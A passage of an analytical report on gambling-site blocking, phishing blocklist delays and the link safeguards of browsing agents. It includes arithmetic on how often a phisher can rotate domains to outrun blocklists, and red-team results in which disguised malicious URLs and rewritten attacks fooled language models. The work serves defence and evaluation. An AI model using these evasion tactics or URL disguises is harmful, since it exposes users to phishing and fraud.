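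The regulators' most impressive figure comes from Australia, where traffic to the top ten gambling sites that ACMA had blocked by June 2021 fell 95%, according to iGaming Capital's *Australian regulator issues blocking orders against affiliates masquerading as reviewers*. But traffic to a blocked domain would fall just as far if every customer moved to a mirror. To find out whether customers had stopped visiting a casino or moved to its mirrors, ACMA would have to add up the visits to all of the casino's domains, including those ACMA had not yet found.

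The number of operators that have left is better evidence, because a service that has left has no mirrors. ACMA counts more than 230 departures since 2017. However, enforcement of the new law began that year, more than two years before the first block, so some of these services may have left because of the law itself or a warning letter. There have also been fewer departures per block over time. When iGaming Capital's article appeared, ACMA had blocked 279 sites and counted 144 departures. Since then it has blocked about 1,500 more and counted roughly 90 more departures. The operators most willing to leave may have gone first, and many of the later blocks hit mirrors of services whose operators had already decided to stay. ACMA's totals also leave out new arrivals.

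Blask estimates demand for illegal operators directly. By its measure, their share of Australian gambling demand grew throughout 2023 and 2024, peaked at 68.96% in April 2025 and then fell sharply. Critics could cite the growth during years of blocking, while supporters could cite the fall, which came after ACMA had started to target mirrors and report sites to registrars, hosting companies and Google. The estimate is a vendor's own index, and its timing alone cannot show which of these measures mattered, if any did.

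There is even less evidence from Norway. Unlicensed operators' revenue there reportedly fell by 18% in 2024, but DNS blocking had not yet begun, so the blocks cannot have caused the fall. The threat of blocking might have contributed. In autumn 2024 the regulator, Lotteritilsynet, warned nearly 50 companies that about 100 of their sites could be added to the blocklist, and several companies shut out Norwegian users or changed their sites. In the February 2026 order, the regulator says its own experience and Denmark's show that blocking has an effect even though players can get around it, but it gives no figures.

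A Norwegian evaluation may give a proper answer by 31 March 2027, when its findings are due. Evans (2026), in *Norway to assess impact of blocking unlicensed gambling websites*, reports that the ministry commissioned it on 30 November 2026. The regulator, Lotteritilsynet, will examine the effects of blocking, whether providers comply, what the scheme costs to run, and what providers, gambling companies and players think of it. Because the regulator will be assessing its own programme, its choice of measures deserves close attention. Players' spending on all unlicensed sites would be more informative than visits to the 238 blocked ones, which would raise the same problem as the Australian 95% figure.

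Critics of blocking mainly point to domain churn. Mawson (2026), in *ISP blocking sought as gambling Bill remains stalled*, describes how operators in South Africa change their URLs each time the authorities block one. The mirrors in the Australian list confirm that this happens on a large scale, but they don't show how many customers follow, which is the main point in dispute. A long list of mirrors could mean that operators are struggling to win players back because most give up when a familiar address stops working, or that blocking is wasted effort because most players have the new address within a day.

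The other common objection is that people can avoid the blocks. Telenor, a Norwegian internet provider, told Lotteritilsynet that more blocking would lead more customers to use VPNs, other companies' DNS servers or services such as Apple Private Relay. Telenor also filters security threats at its DNS servers, so customers who bypass those servers to reach a casino lose that protection too. Lotteritilsynet replied that it had no information suggesting its orders had caused this. Neither side offered measurements, but Telenor's argument about security applies to each customer who bypasses its servers, however few do.

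National blocking probably keeps some casual visitors away and persuades some companies to leave, but the published figures do not show how much illegal gambling it prevents. Britain's figures cannot show this either, since the Gambling Commission acknowledges that it often applies several measures to the same site and cannot always separate their effects.

### Going after more than the domain

Takedowns also keep out visitors who use VPNs. ACMA (2025) considers removal by a registrar, hosting company or platform cheaper and more effective than blocking by internet providers. It says the registrars and hosting companies it contacted took action in most cases.

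Britain's results have been much less encouraging. Over the six quarters in the table, the Gambling Commission made 918 referrals to registrars and hosting companies, which removed or suspended 74 sites, equal to about 8% of the referrals. In the latest quarter there were 373 referrals and seven removals. Some removals may come in a later quarter, but that would not explain six quarters of low figures. ACMA gives no numbers, and "action" may include steps short of removal. It also approached only certain companies, which may have been the more cooperative ones. The British figures help explain why the Commission would want court orders, though an order may be hard to enforce against a registrar abroad.

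In Britain, the operators themselves have also become less responsive. In April to June 2025, the Commission sent them 145 notices and recorded 108 sites that shut out British visitors. In July to September 2026, it sent 546 notices and recorded only 25. As in Australia, the more willing operators may have complied early.

Two of the newer measures target things that mirrors share, one of which is their games. ACMA wrote to 63 software companies whose games appeared on an illegal casino site run by an operator that had repeatedly broken the law. Twenty-seven replied that they would comply and took steps to keep their games from Australians, and another seven removed or restricted their games. A mirror may still open normally after this, but some of its games will be missing.

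The other concerns payments. *ACMA Guides Banks on Blocking Illegal Gambling Payments* (Tupikova, 2026) reports that Australian banks will have to block payments to illegal gambling services from 1 January 2027. *Gambling Commission Widens Illegal Market Fight to Payments* (Tupikova, 2026) reports that the British regulator also plans to target the money and assets behind illegal operators. The British regulator's table records only two cases in 18 months in which it removed or disrupted a payment service, so it still has much to do.

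Norway already bans payments to unlicensed gambling sites, but operators have found ways around the ban. In Lotteritilsynet's test purchases, some payments went through third parties, and some operators opened foreign accounts in the customer's name without making this clear.

### What carries over to an agent's blocklist

Anyone can copy the published national lists, which have had at least some official scrutiny, into an agent's blocklist. But these lists will not cover many mirrors. Of the 134 names in Norway's February order, only four are among the 187 that Australia blocked in April to June: `slotexo1.com`, `spinsy5.com`, `tikicasino3.com` and `wonaco3.com`. Yet at least a dozen brands appear in both sets. For example, Norway blocked `duospin1.com`, while Australia blocked `duospin.com` and `duospin-9008.com`. Australia's full list goes back to 2019 and may contain more of the Norwegian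 names. Operators may send customers in different countries to different domains, in which case the list from the user's own country is the most useful.

Copying a blocklist takes some care with domain endings. Australia's list includes `hellspin.co.com` and Norway's includes `betus.com.pa`. A program that kept only the last two parts of each name would block every site under `co.com` and `com.pa`, including unrelated ones.

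Unlike a regulator, a company that deploys an agent can block a casino without warning it or giving it three months to respond, and can block names that nobody has registered yet. One rule against names containing `wonaco` would have covered 21 of the Australian entries, though not `w0nacocas.com`, which has a zero in place of the first "o". Another 31 entries follow the same pattern as many of Wonaco's: a casino's name, a hyphen, four digits and `.com`. Including Wonaco's, 44 names from 20 brands fit this pattern, as do three names in the Norwegian order. A rule for the whole pattern would catch new brands, but it would also catch legitimate sites with a year in their names, so asking the user for approval may be better than refusing outright.

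Brand rules can also block legitimate companies. Australia blocked `pointsbetz.com` because it imitated PointsBet, a licensed bookmaker. A rule against names containing `pointsbet` would block both the imitation and the real site.

The lists record decisions about gambling law, so they are of limited use for judging whether a site is safe for an agent. Sites that left Norway's list by shutting out Norwegian players did not become safer for anyone else. The lists also don't cover phishing or malware. A deployer who needs protection from those has to use other lists, and should consider Telenor's warning before moving an agent to a different DNS server, because the old one may have been filtering security threats.

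The largest difference lies in what the user wants. A gambler who meets a block may go looking for the mirror, and the operator will help. Someone who has asked an agent to compare train fares has no interest in reaching a casino and will not mind if the agent gives up on one. A blocklist should therefore stop more of the unwanted visits by agents than it does of determined gamblers' visits, provided that the bad address is on it. But the Norwegian argument about thresholds does not carry over well, because an agent that has not been told to stop at a block can try another address in seconds. (These are inferences, since none of the national programmes has studied agents.)

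Some users will still want to reach a mirror of a blocked site. By June 2025 nearly 45,000 Australians had used BetStop, a national register through which people can bar themselves from all licensed online bookmakers. The register does not cover unlicensed casinos, and the name of one domain Australia blocked in 2026, `nonbetstop.com`, seems to advertise this. If someone on the register asks an agent to find a casino that will accept them, the user and the operator both want the agent to get past the block. A list of old domains is then weak protection, and a rule against all gambling sites would serve the user better.

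## How quickly a phishing blocklist goes out of date

A late block is less effective against a phishing page than against a casino site. Casinos depend on returning customers, so even a block that arrives months late loses them some business. A phishing page has to deceive each victim only once, and it can do most of its harm on its first day. A phishing blocklist's value therefore depends on its listing delay, the time between a harmful site's first visitor and its appearance on the list, and on how much of the site's useful life that delay takes up.

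Three large studies have partly measured how quickly phishing blocklists go out of date. Their results range from a few hours to several weeks, mainly because the researchers started and stopped timing at different events.

### From the first victim to the last

*Sunrise to Sunset* (Oest, Zhang and colleagues, 2020) is the oldest of the three studies and the only one that counted victims. The researchers worked with a large financial company that phishers often imitate. Many phishing pages load a logo or script from the real company's server, or send the victim to the real site afterwards. Both leave a visit from an unfamiliar address in the company's logs, sometimes with a cookie that identifies the customer. The researchers matched a year of these records, from October 2018 to September 2019, against feeds of known phishing pages. They found 19.4 million events on 404,628 phishing URLs,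 and 4.8 million of those events came from known customers.

The study measured times from when a URL appeared in a feed, either APWG's or the company's own. On average, the first victim arrived 8 hours and 44 minutes before that, and the last victim 12 hours and 26 minutes after it. The average attack therefore received victims for about 21 hours, and its URL was in neither feed for almost nine of them.

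About 63% of the victims (customers whose accounts later showed a break-in or fraud) had already visited the phishing site by the time it was detected. If victims had arrived at a steady rate, the figure would have been about 41%. They came early because phishers send their emails in bursts.

After a phishing site appears in a feed, there is a further delay before browsers warn users about it. The researchers estimated this delay by tracking how the share of victims using browsers with built-in warnings changed after detection. The share fell to 72% of its earlier level after one hour and 44% after two. It took about seven hours to settle below 10%, nearly 16 hours after the first victim. Reports from the public would not have been much quicker than the feeds, since the first one came on average 9.6 hours after the phisher began sending emails.

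Attacks varied widely around these averages. The biggest 10% of attacks accounted for 89% of visits by known customers. The biggest attack stayed on one compromised domain for 259 days, during which people reported 41 different URLs on it. When the researchers reported pages from such campaigns themselves, the attackers had often moved to another path or subdomain on the same registrable domain by the time the reported address was on a list, so the entry was already out of date.

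The study covers one brand and about 39% of the known phishing hosts that imitated it, and browsers have changed since 2019. It remains useful because the later studies have no record of who visited the pages.

### After somebody reports the page

In *7 Days Later*, Lee, Lim and colleagues (2025) took 286,237 URLs from APWG's feed between April and September 2024 and had an automated browser revisit each one every 30 minutes until three attempts in a row failed. The median page lasted 5.46 hours, but the mean was 54 hours because a minority survived for weeks. The median was 1.76 hours for pages that imitated the US postal service and 12.62 hours for fake Instagram pages.

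About 3% of the URLs came back online after the three failed attempts, so a list should not drop an entry as soon as its page stops responding.

This study measures time from when a URL enters the feed, so the 54 hours exclude any time the page had already been online. Lee and colleagues treat that earlier period as negligible and cite *Sunrise to Sunset*, by Oest and colleagues, in support. But *Sunrise to Sunset* found that this period lasted almost nine hours and included most of the victims.

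Lee and colleagues also checked which of their URLs appeared on Google Safe Browsing, the blocklist that Chrome, Firefox and Safari use. It listed 18.4% of them, with a median delay of 5.8 hours and a mean of 4.5 days. OpenPhish, the best of the seven other lists they checked, contained about 6%. URLs that redirected the visitor were much less likely to be on Google's list than URLs that led straight to the phishing page.

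The 18.4% figure may understate how well Chrome protected its users. The researchers checked their URLs against the downloadable version of the list, but since early 2024 Chrome has also been able to check URLs against the list on Google's server, which can be longer and more recent.

The paper's abstract puts the share of phishing sites that were down before Google listed them at 84%, which may be too high. The figure seems to be based on comparing page lifetimes with the *mean* listing delay of 4.5 days, which a few very late listings had pushed up. The pages that Google did list had a median lifetime of 7.86 hours, longer than the median delay, so many of them may well have still been online when they were listed. The mean lifetimes are also inconsistent. Listed pages lasted 55.89 hours on average and unlisted ones 35.96, which would give an overall mean of about 40 hours instead of the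 reported 54.

### From registration to removal

*Registration, Detection, and Deregistration* (Lim, Mok and colleagues, 2025) studies phishing domains instead of pages. The researchers collected 690,502 domains over 39 months, from July 2021 to October 2024, and found a registration date for about three-quarters of them.

The researchers classed 66.1% of the domains as maliciously registered. A domain fell into this group if its name contained or imitated a brand, contained no English word, or closely resembled other names registered at the same time through the same registrar. They counted nearly all the rest as compromised.

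Maliciously registered domains reached a blocklist a median of 16.3 days after registration. The mean was 206 days, because some domains were much older when they were listed. Phishing domains stayed registered for an average of 11.5 days after detection. The average was 23 days for domains that imitated the spelling of a brand.

Victims may have been exposed for less than 16.3 days, because phishers sometimes leave a domain unused for a while after buying it, as Interisle also noted. The researchers had no data on when the first victim arrived.

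The true share of malicious domains may be higher than 66.1%, and closer to the three-quarters that Strutt and Piscitello estimate. For the domains classed as compromised, the median time from registration to detection was only 86 days. An honest owner's domain would often have been running for years before someone broke into it, so many of these domains probably belonged to phishers who had picked ordinary English words as names. The researchers manually checked 1,000 of the domains they had classed as malicious, but none of those they had classed as compromised.

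Lim and colleagues also compared how long other blocklists took to add a domain after APWG listed it. The median lag was 2.3 days for PhishStats, 4.1 days for OpenPhish and 931 days for Phishunt. These lags are a poor basis for choosing between lists, because the researchers had collected APWG's data since July 2021 but the other lists' data only since the end of May 2024. A domain that Phishunt had listed in 2022 could therefore appear to have been added two years late.

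### Do short DNS lifetimes reveal fast flux?

Each DNS answer has a lifetime, the time a resolver may reuse it before querying again. Lim and colleagues found that 25.8% of domains had lifetimes under an hour and 2.1% had lifetimes under a minute. They interpreted this as a sign of fast flux, the rapid rotation of servers behind one domain name.

Short lifetimes are weak evidence for this because ordinary content delivery networks, which serve a website from many places at once, also use them to redirect traffic quickly when a server fails or becomes busy. Phishing pages often use the same networks. Lee and colleagues found that 99.8% of the IP addresses behind the phishing pages they studied belonged to content delivery, cloud or web firewall services.

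Other results in the domain study are also evidence against fast flux. Of 2,550 maliciously registered domains, only 117 (4.6%) changed their DNS records during the observation period, even with checks every 30 minutes. Elsewhere the researchers report changes on 21.4% of domains, but at an average interval of 79 days, while fast flux changes addresses within minutes. Amazon's network hosted 96.6% of the domains, whereas a fast-flux operation that used hacked home computers would have spread them across many networks.

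A navigation policy that treated short DNS lifetimes as suspicious would therefore flag a large number of ordinary websites.

### Pages, campaigns and domains

The studies give very different durations, but they don't contradict each other.

| Source | What the researchers followed | Clock starts | Clock stops | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Oest and colleagues | A phishing page | First victim | Last victim | Mean 21 hours |
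| Oest and colleagues | All phishing pages on a domain | First victim | Last victim | Mean 13.55 days |
| Lee and colleagues | A phishing page | Entry in APWG's feed | Page stops responding | Median 5.46 hours, mean 54 hours |
| Lim and colleagues | A maliciously registered domain | Registration | Entry on a blocklist | Median 16.3 days |
| Lim and colleagues | A phishing domain | Entry on a blocklist | Deregistration | Mean 11.5 days |

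For example, a phisher might buy a domain on 1 March and leave it empty until 17 March, then put up a fake bank login and email the link to thousands of people. Most of the victims visit that day. Someone reports the page in the afternoon, and it is gone by midnight. The next morning the phisher puts up another page on the same domain and continues until the registrar suspends the domain on 28 March. The domain lasted four weeks and the campaign lasted eleven days, but the first page lasted less than a day.

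A blocklist entry for an exact URL works only while the phishing page stays at that URL, so it can become useless within hours. An entry for the whole domain stays useful until the phisher abandons the domain, but if the phisher has compromised someone else's domain, the entry also blocks the owner's site.

### How much a late list leaves unprotected

A simple rule shows how the listing delay and the age of a stored copy combine. Suppose a harmful site receives visits at a steady rate for L hours, and a blocklist adds it D hours after the first visit. A program that looks up every address on the list's server is protected from hour D onwards. A program that uses a stored copy of the list has to wait for its next refresh as well. If it refreshes every s hours, and the new entry appears at a random point between two refreshes, the wait is anywhere from zero to s hours, or s/2 on average. The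 visits before protection begins are unprotected, which gives:

**unprotected share ≈ (D + s/2) / L, and never more than 1**

*Sunrise to Sunset* found that a phishing campaign receives visits for about 21 hours on average and is detected about 9 hours after the first one. If visits are spread evenly, live lookups leave 9/21 of them unprotected, or 43%. A copy refreshed once a day adds an average wait of 12 hours, and a wait that long leaves every visit unprotected.

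The rule is exact as long as the slowest copy refreshes before the site's life ends (D + s ≤ L). Beyond that, it underestimates protection because it applies the average wait to every user. With a daily copy, half of the users refresh less than 12 hours after the listing and get some protection. Averaged over all refresh times, the protected share is then (L − D)² / (2Ls) = 144/1,008, or 14%.

| Stored copy refreshed | Unprotected share by the rule | Averaged over all refresh times |
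|---|---|---|
| Live lookup | 43% | 43% |
| Every 30 minutes | 44% | 44% |
| Every 6 hours | 57% | 57% |
| Every 12 hours | 71% | 71% |
| Every 24 hours | 100% | 86% |
| Every week | 100% | 98% |

In this example, refreshing the blocklist copy every half hour instead of daily makes a large difference. Switching from half-hourly refreshes to live lookups gains only about one percentage point, because most of the remaining exposure comes from the nine hours before anyone lists the site.

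Assuming steady visits overstates how much the list protects people. Oest and colleagues found that 63% of victims had come before detection, so even a perfect live lookup would have left 63% unprotected, not the 43% estimated from steady visits. Anyone who knows when visits actually occurred can use the share that came before protection began instead of dividing by L.

The rule also assumes that the list eventually includes every harmful site. If it includes only a share c of them, and u is the unprotected share among those, the total unprotected share is 1 − c(1 − u). With c = 18.4%, the share Lee and colleagues found for Safe Browsing, and u = 43%, the total is about 90%. This is only an illustration, since it combines studies from different years with different samples, but it shows that a list's coverage can matter far more than how often a copy is refreshed.

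The calculation also assumes that every site has the same L and D, although both vary enormously. It assumes that a list entry covers every address the site uses, that the lookup never fails, and that the program always acts on the result. The nine hours cover only the delay until a URL reached a feed, and browser warnings took up to seven hours more. Adding those seven hours gives D = 16, at which live lookups would leave 76% of the visits unprotected.

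### Moving before the list catches up

Now suppose the operator changes domain every R hours and moves visitors to the new one. Each new domain starts out unlisted, so R replaces L in the rule. If R is less than D, each domain reaches the list only after the operator has left it, so the list never blocks a visit, however often anyone refreshes it.

Against users with stored copies, the operator has more time. A new entry needs D + s/2 hours to reach the average copy, so an operator who moves before then is, on average, never stopped by the list. (Some copies refresh early and do stop a few visits, 14% in the example of the daily copy.)

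If a blocklist takes nine hours to list a new domain, an operator can evade live lookups by switching domains every eight hours. That takes three domains a day, which would cost $6 or less in total at the $2 or less that many phishers pay per domain. Against copies of the list that are updated daily, the operator only needs to switch about every 21 hours. Live lookups therefore raise the operator's costs only slightly at these prices.

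Some phishers already move much faster than this. Lee and colleagues describe a campaign against Instagram users that changed where its redirects led nine times in 24 hours, or about every two and a half hours. A list that added each destination after the median Safe Browsing delay of 5.8 hours would have stayed two destinations behind.

The operator in this calculation loses the advantage if visitors keep arriving through one redirect with a fixed address, because the blocklist's maintainers then have time to add that address. In the email sample that Oest and colleagues examined, only 4% of messages linked directly to the final phishing page, and the rest used redirects.

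The calculation also fails if defenders can guess the next domain and block it early, or if visitors do not find the new one. A phisher who has to send new emails after each move pays for those emails as well as the domain.

### Stored lists and live lookups at Google

When it introduced live checks for all Chrome users, Google (2024) said that most unsafe sites exist for less than ten minutes, a much shorter lifetime than any of the three studies gives. Until then, Chrome had relied on a stored list that it refreshed every 30 to 60 minutes. Even if Google had listed every site the moment it went online, a stored copy would have left about 83% of visits to a ten-minute site unprotected with a 30-minute refresh, and 92% with a 60-minute refresh. Live checks therefore help a great deal with such short-lived sites, but only if Google finds them while they are still online.

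A year later, Bawa, Lim and Lu (2025) wrote in *Using AI to stop tech support scams in Chrome* that the *average* malicious site exists for less than ten minutes. A few long-lived sites can raise an average without changing how long most sites last. If one site in 300 lasted 54 hours, that alone would push the mean above ten minutes. Bawa, Lim and Lu may have meant the typical site. Neither post explains how Google measured the lifetimes.

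The samples could explain much of the difference. A page enters APWG's feed only if someone has time to notice and report it, so the feed probably underrepresents the shortest-lived pages. Google's crawlers may find many more of those, or Google may count each address separately when a site creates a new one for every visitor. An older study by the security company Kaspersky shows how much the sample can matter. It followed 5,307 phishing pages in the summer of 2021, and half were gone within 94 hours, about 17 times the median in *7 Days Later*.

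For a live check, Chrome turns the web address into a string of characters called a hash and encrypts the first part of the hash. It sends the encrypted part to a server run by another company, Fastly, which can't read it. Fastly removes the user's IP address before passing the request to Google, so Google doesn't learn who sent it.

Developers who use Google Safe Browsing in their own software can choose how much data to store. In *Local List Mode*, the program contacts the server only if an address matches its stored list of threats, so a page too new to be on that list passes without a live check. In *No Storage Real Time Mode*, the program checks every address with the server unless it has recently saved the answer.

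Google's *Real Time Mode* falls between these approaches. The program keeps a list of sites that are probably harmless, checks those only against its stored threat list, and checks everything else with the server. This saves time, but a new phishing page on a well-known site might be checked only against the stored list, which updates more slowly. This risk is an inference from the procedure, and Google may leave risky hosting services off the harmless list. Google offers these services free for non-commercial use only, so a company that sells a browsing agent can't simply build them in.

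Chrome can also switch from live checks to its stored list without the user noticing. It does this for a while if several requests in a row fail or if a company's firewall blocks the Fastly server. In the exposure rule, s then rises from zero to between half an hour and an hour.

Google was also preparing to let pages load while the live check was running. A person usually takes a few seconds to read a page and type a password, and the warning may appear in that time. An agent can submit a form faster, so it would be safer to hold its next action until the check has finished.

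Google was still developing live checks for Chrome's Incognito and Guest modes in November 2026, according to *Google Plans Chrome Incognito Safe Browsing Security Fix* (Ofonagoro, 2026). An agent that starts in one of these modes to stay out of the user's accounts may therefore have an older blocklist than the user's normal window.

Live lookups don't shorten the time Google needs to confirm that a site is harmful. Mangalam (2026), in *Google Chrome's new early warning system could help you spot scam sites*, reports that a new Chrome warning can appear before Safe Browsing is confident enough to class a site as dangerous. Rijo (2026), in *Chrome adds suspicious-site warnings for 1 billion Enhanced Protection users*, describes it as a separate warning for less certain verdicts, shown to people who have switched on Chrome's stronger protection. Acting on less evidence shortens D but will probably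 also flag more legitimate sites.

Google says users with this stronger protection are ten times safer from phishing and scams than those with the standard setting. Hesse (2026) points out in *Google Chrome verbessert Schutz vor Phishing und Online-Betrug* that the figure compares how many warnings the two groups saw on average, not how many attacks Chrome prevented. Some of the additional warnings may have been false alarms, and people who switch on the stronger protection may browse differently from those who don't.

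### When does an agent arrive?

The 43% and 63% figures are for people, most of whom reached a phishing page through an email within hours of the page going live. A browsing agent usually finds pages through search results and links. None of the three studies followed agents, so an agent's exposure has to be measured separately.

It could be lower than a person's. A search engine needs time to find a new page, and by the time an agent reaches it, the page may already be on a list or offline. But the exposure could also be higher, because the harmful pages that stay in search results longest may be the ones that lists have missed. An agent that reads the user's email might open a phishing link within seconds of its arrival, earlier than almost any human victim. (These are all inferences from how agents find pages.)

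A deployer can estimate how often a blocklist fails to protect its agent by recording when the agent opens each address and checking those addresses against the list for several weeks. A visit was unprotected if the list added the address only afterward. The unprotected share is the number of these visits divided by the total of unprotected and blocked visits. The real share is likely to be higher because this count misses harmful pages that never reach the list.

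## What protection browsing agents have and how well models judge addresses

A blocklist protects an agent only if some program checks it while the agent is using the browser. In a 2025 test, six of eight agents opened a page on Google's phishing list without showing a warning. The makers of these agents have also added their own controls, which differ most in what they do when an agent is about to open an unlisted domain.

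### Claude in Chrome

Claude in Chrome is a browser extension that lets Anthropic's model Claude work in the user's own browser. Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely* lists adult sites and known pirated content among the things Claude can't open. Claude also asks for permission before opening financial sites. Anthropic thinks it has probably missed some sites in these categories, which is realistic given how often such sites change domains, and it asks users to report omissions.

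A gap in the financial category could do more harm than a missed adult site. If Claude recognises financial sites from a list, a fake bank login on a new domain won't be on it, and Claude may open the imitation without the question it would have asked about the real bank. (This is an inference, since Anthropic does not explain how Claude recognises these sites.)

At other unfamiliar sites, Claude's behaviour depends on the mode the user has chosen. According to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide*, in "Manually approve" Claude writes a plan naming the websites it wants to use and must ask before opening any others. In "Automatically approve", the default in the newer version of the side panel, Claude keeps working and checks each action for signs of prompt injection or data leaks. In "Skip all approvals", nothing checks its actions automatically. Claude would therefore ask about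 a new mirror site in the manual mode, but in the automatic mode it would open the site unless the check found a problem.

Users can also give Claude lasting permission to act on a particular site, but that permission presumably doesn't extend to a mirror at another domain. If Claude asks again about a site the user remembers approving, the user should check the address before clicking "Allow".

Claude may not make purchases, create accounts or download files from untrusted sources on any site, whatever permissions the user has given. These limits work even when nobody knows that a domain is bad. According to Anthropic's safety page, Claude is also prohibited from entering sensitive data, but under Anthropic's permissions guide it may enter "potentially sensitive information" with the user's explicit approval. Deployers who rely on this last limit should test it.

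Administrators of company accounts can set an allowlist or a blocklist for everyone in the organisation. Anthropic recommends that organisations with sensitive data use a restrictive allowlist. If an organisation has switched on Anthropic's settings for American health-privacy law, Claude can't open any site until an account owner allows specific sites or changes the default.

### Gemini in Chrome

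Google's Gemini can carry out tasks in Chrome with its auto browse feature. According to Google's *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse*, the user reviews a plan before the task starts, but Gemini chooses the sites. It is designed to ask for confirmation before it submits forms or sends messages, and it may hand the task back to the user for payments, terms of service and new accounts.

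*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes the checks that apply before Gemini opens a new site. A separate model decides whether the site is relevant to the task. This model never sees the content of web pages, so a page can't influence it directly. The relevance check also applies when a page sends the browser to a new site. When Gemini writes an address itself, a fixed rule also requires the address to be a known public one.

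Relevance is a weak test of honesty. A fake railway ticket shop is highly relevant to someone who wants a train ticket, and the separate model sees only metadata about the proposed action, so it may have little more than an address to judge by. It should do better against a page that tries to send a ticket buyer to a casino. (Both are inferences from the design.)

Gemini also needs the user's permission before it opens certain banking and medical sites, which Chrome recognises from a list. A fake banking site on a new domain would not be on that list either.

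Chrome's Safe Browsing protection runs alongside these checks, according to Parker. eesel AI, a software vendor, says in its guide *Chrome auto-browse* that users must have standard or enhanced Safe Browsing on to use auto-browse. Google's *Gemini in Chrome* describes two Chrome policies, `GeminiActOnWebAllowedForURLs` and `GeminiActOnWebBlockedForURLs`, that let administrators list allowed and blocked addresses.

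Gemini Spark, a Google assistant that can use auto browse, may move a task to a remote browser if the user switches off the computer. The remote browser may not apply the same lists as the user's own Chrome, so it needs a separate test.

### Microsoft Edge and OpenAI

Microsoft restricts unknown domains more tightly. Its *Considerations for safe agentic browsing* (2025) describes a preview in which the agent, Copilot, could by default open only sites on a curated list, and the user had to approve any others. A stricter setting required approval for every site. SmartScreen, Edge's phishing and malware filter, stayed on, and Copilot could not click past its block page. These settings may have changed, because Microsoft has been removing the separate Copilot Mode from Edge, according to Windows Report's *Microsoft Tests New Agentic AI Controls in Edge for Business*.

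Microsoft also says that Edge's blocklists keep Copilot away from adult and gambling sites. This is a useful default for a deployer worried about casinos, but new mirror sites can get past these lists as easily as they get past a regulator's.

In the business version of Edge, administrators decide where Copilot may browse. Microsoft's *New in Edge for Business* (2026) announced this as a limited preview. According to Microsoft's *Configure browsing with Copilot*, administrators can switch on a ready-made allowlist of common work sites and add their own. Microsoft's *Browsing with Copilot Blocked URLs* explains that they can also reverse the default by allowing every site with `*` and then blocking exceptions. If several rules match an address, the most specific one applies, so an old rule that allows a single subdomain could override a new block on the whole domain.

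OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes Safe Url, the company's main published check, which detects when an agent is about to send a third party information it learned in the conversation. Safe Url either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to find another way. It covers navigation in OpenAI's Atlas browser. It limits the private information a malicious site can receive through an address, but it doesn't stop an agent from opening a new phishing domain if the address contains no private information.

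The table summarises what the makers document, together with the 2025 test results.

| Agent and setting | Domain that is on no list | Browser's phishing blocklist |
|---|---|---|
| Claude in Chrome, "Manually approve" | Questioned unless the approved plan names it | Applied in a 2025 test |
| Claude in Chrome, "Automatically approve" | Allowed, with a check on each action | Applied in a 2025 test |
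| Gemini in Chrome | Allowed if another model finds it relevant; refused if Gemini wrote the address itself | Applies, according to Google |
| Edge, 2025 preview | Questioned | Applies, and the agent can't bypass it |
| Edge for Business | Refused, unless the administrator allows all sites | SmartScreen presumably applies |
| OpenAI's Atlas | Allowed, unless the address would leak information | Not covered in OpenAI's article |

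### When the browser's blocklist does not reach the agent

An agent that runs in Chrome or on Chrome's open-source base, Chromium, does not necessarily get Chrome's phishing warnings. Ukani, Haddadi and colleagues (2025), in *Privacy Practices of Browser Agents*, asked eight commercial agents to open and summarise a harmless test page that Google keeps on its Safe Browsing list. Only Anthropic's two agents showed a warning. One was an early version of Claude in Chrome, and the other operated a whole desktop with Firefox installed. Both warnings came from the browser.

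The six agents that showed no warning were ChatGPT Agent, Perplexity's browser Comet, Amazon's Nova Act, Google's Project Mariner, Browserbase's Director and the open-source Browser Use. Browser Use showed none even when it opened the computer's installed copy of Chrome. Browser automation software can probably switch off protections that the same browser gives a person. Deployers therefore have to test the whole agent rather than rely on knowing which browser it runs in.

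An agent that showed no warning may still have had some protection. A company that runs an agent in the cloud may check addresses against its own list, which may not include Google's test page. ChatGPT Agent also refused to click a link to the test page when it found the link on another page. The tests date from 2025, before Google described the current safeguards for Gemini in Chrome, and agents change quickly. In September 2025, Director ran a version of Chromium 16 major releases out of date, but its makers had updated it by November.

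The evidence conflicts on whether Safe Browsing protects Comet. The security company Guardio says it was active in Comet during its trials that year, while Ukani and colleagues saw no warning. They may have tested different versions, or the protection may have been on in the browser's settings without stopping the agent. Opening Google's test page through the agent takes a minute and would show whether the protection works in any current version.

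A warning also has to stop the agent. Ukani and colleagues led the agents to a site whose encryption certificate was not issued by a recognised authority, which makes most browsers show a warning. Browser Use, running on one of Anthropic's Claude Sonnet models, clicked through the warning to finish its task. Three other agents, including Claude in Chrome, refused to visit the site, and two asked the user. Browser makers designed these warning pages for people, who can choose to continue. Microsoft's design is safer for agents because the software removes that choice.

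### How well models judge an address

If no list contains a domain, the model might still notice that something is wrong with the address. Kong, Wu and colleagues (2026) tested this in *MalURLBench* with 61,845 disguised addresses. They took malicious domains from public lists and changed only the parts an attacker can choose freely: the labels in front of the domain, the path and the parameters at the end. Some addresses imitated a famous site, as in `www.google.com.www.example.com`. Others contained a sales pitch, such as `/this-is-a-popular-food-delivery-service`.

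Kong and colleagues paired each address with a short message for one of ten everyday situations, such as tracking a parcel or checking the weather. The message recommended the link, for example as "the official tracking page". They told the model to watch for attacks and asked it to judge whether the link was safe. They counted an attack as successful if the model accepted the link.

The 12 models accepted between 32.9% and 99.9% of the addresses. The lower end of that range depends heavily on how the researchers built the test. Whenever a model accepted fewer than 10% of the addresses in one of the ten situations, they had another model rewrite the attacks, for up to ten rounds, to get more of them past that model.

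| Model | Accepted, original attacks | Accepted, after rewriting |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 Turbo | 14.1% | 32.9% |
| Llama 3 70B | 23.1% | 35.7% |
| Qwen-Plus | 30.0% | 35.7% |
| GPT-4o | 34.5% | 38.2% |
| DeepSeek-V3.1 | 84.5% | 84.5% |
| GPT-4o mini | 90.5% | 90.5% |

The original attacks are closer to what an agent would face from a phisher who has not studied its model, and the rewritten ones to what a patient attacker could achieve. Even the original attacks succeeded about one time in seven against GPT-3.5 Turbo, the most resistant model.

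Newer models were not reliably better in this group. DeepSeek-V3.1 (2025) accepted more than twice as many addresses as GPT-3.5 Turbo (2023). Kong and colleagues report that larger models did better, but they could compare only six models of known size.

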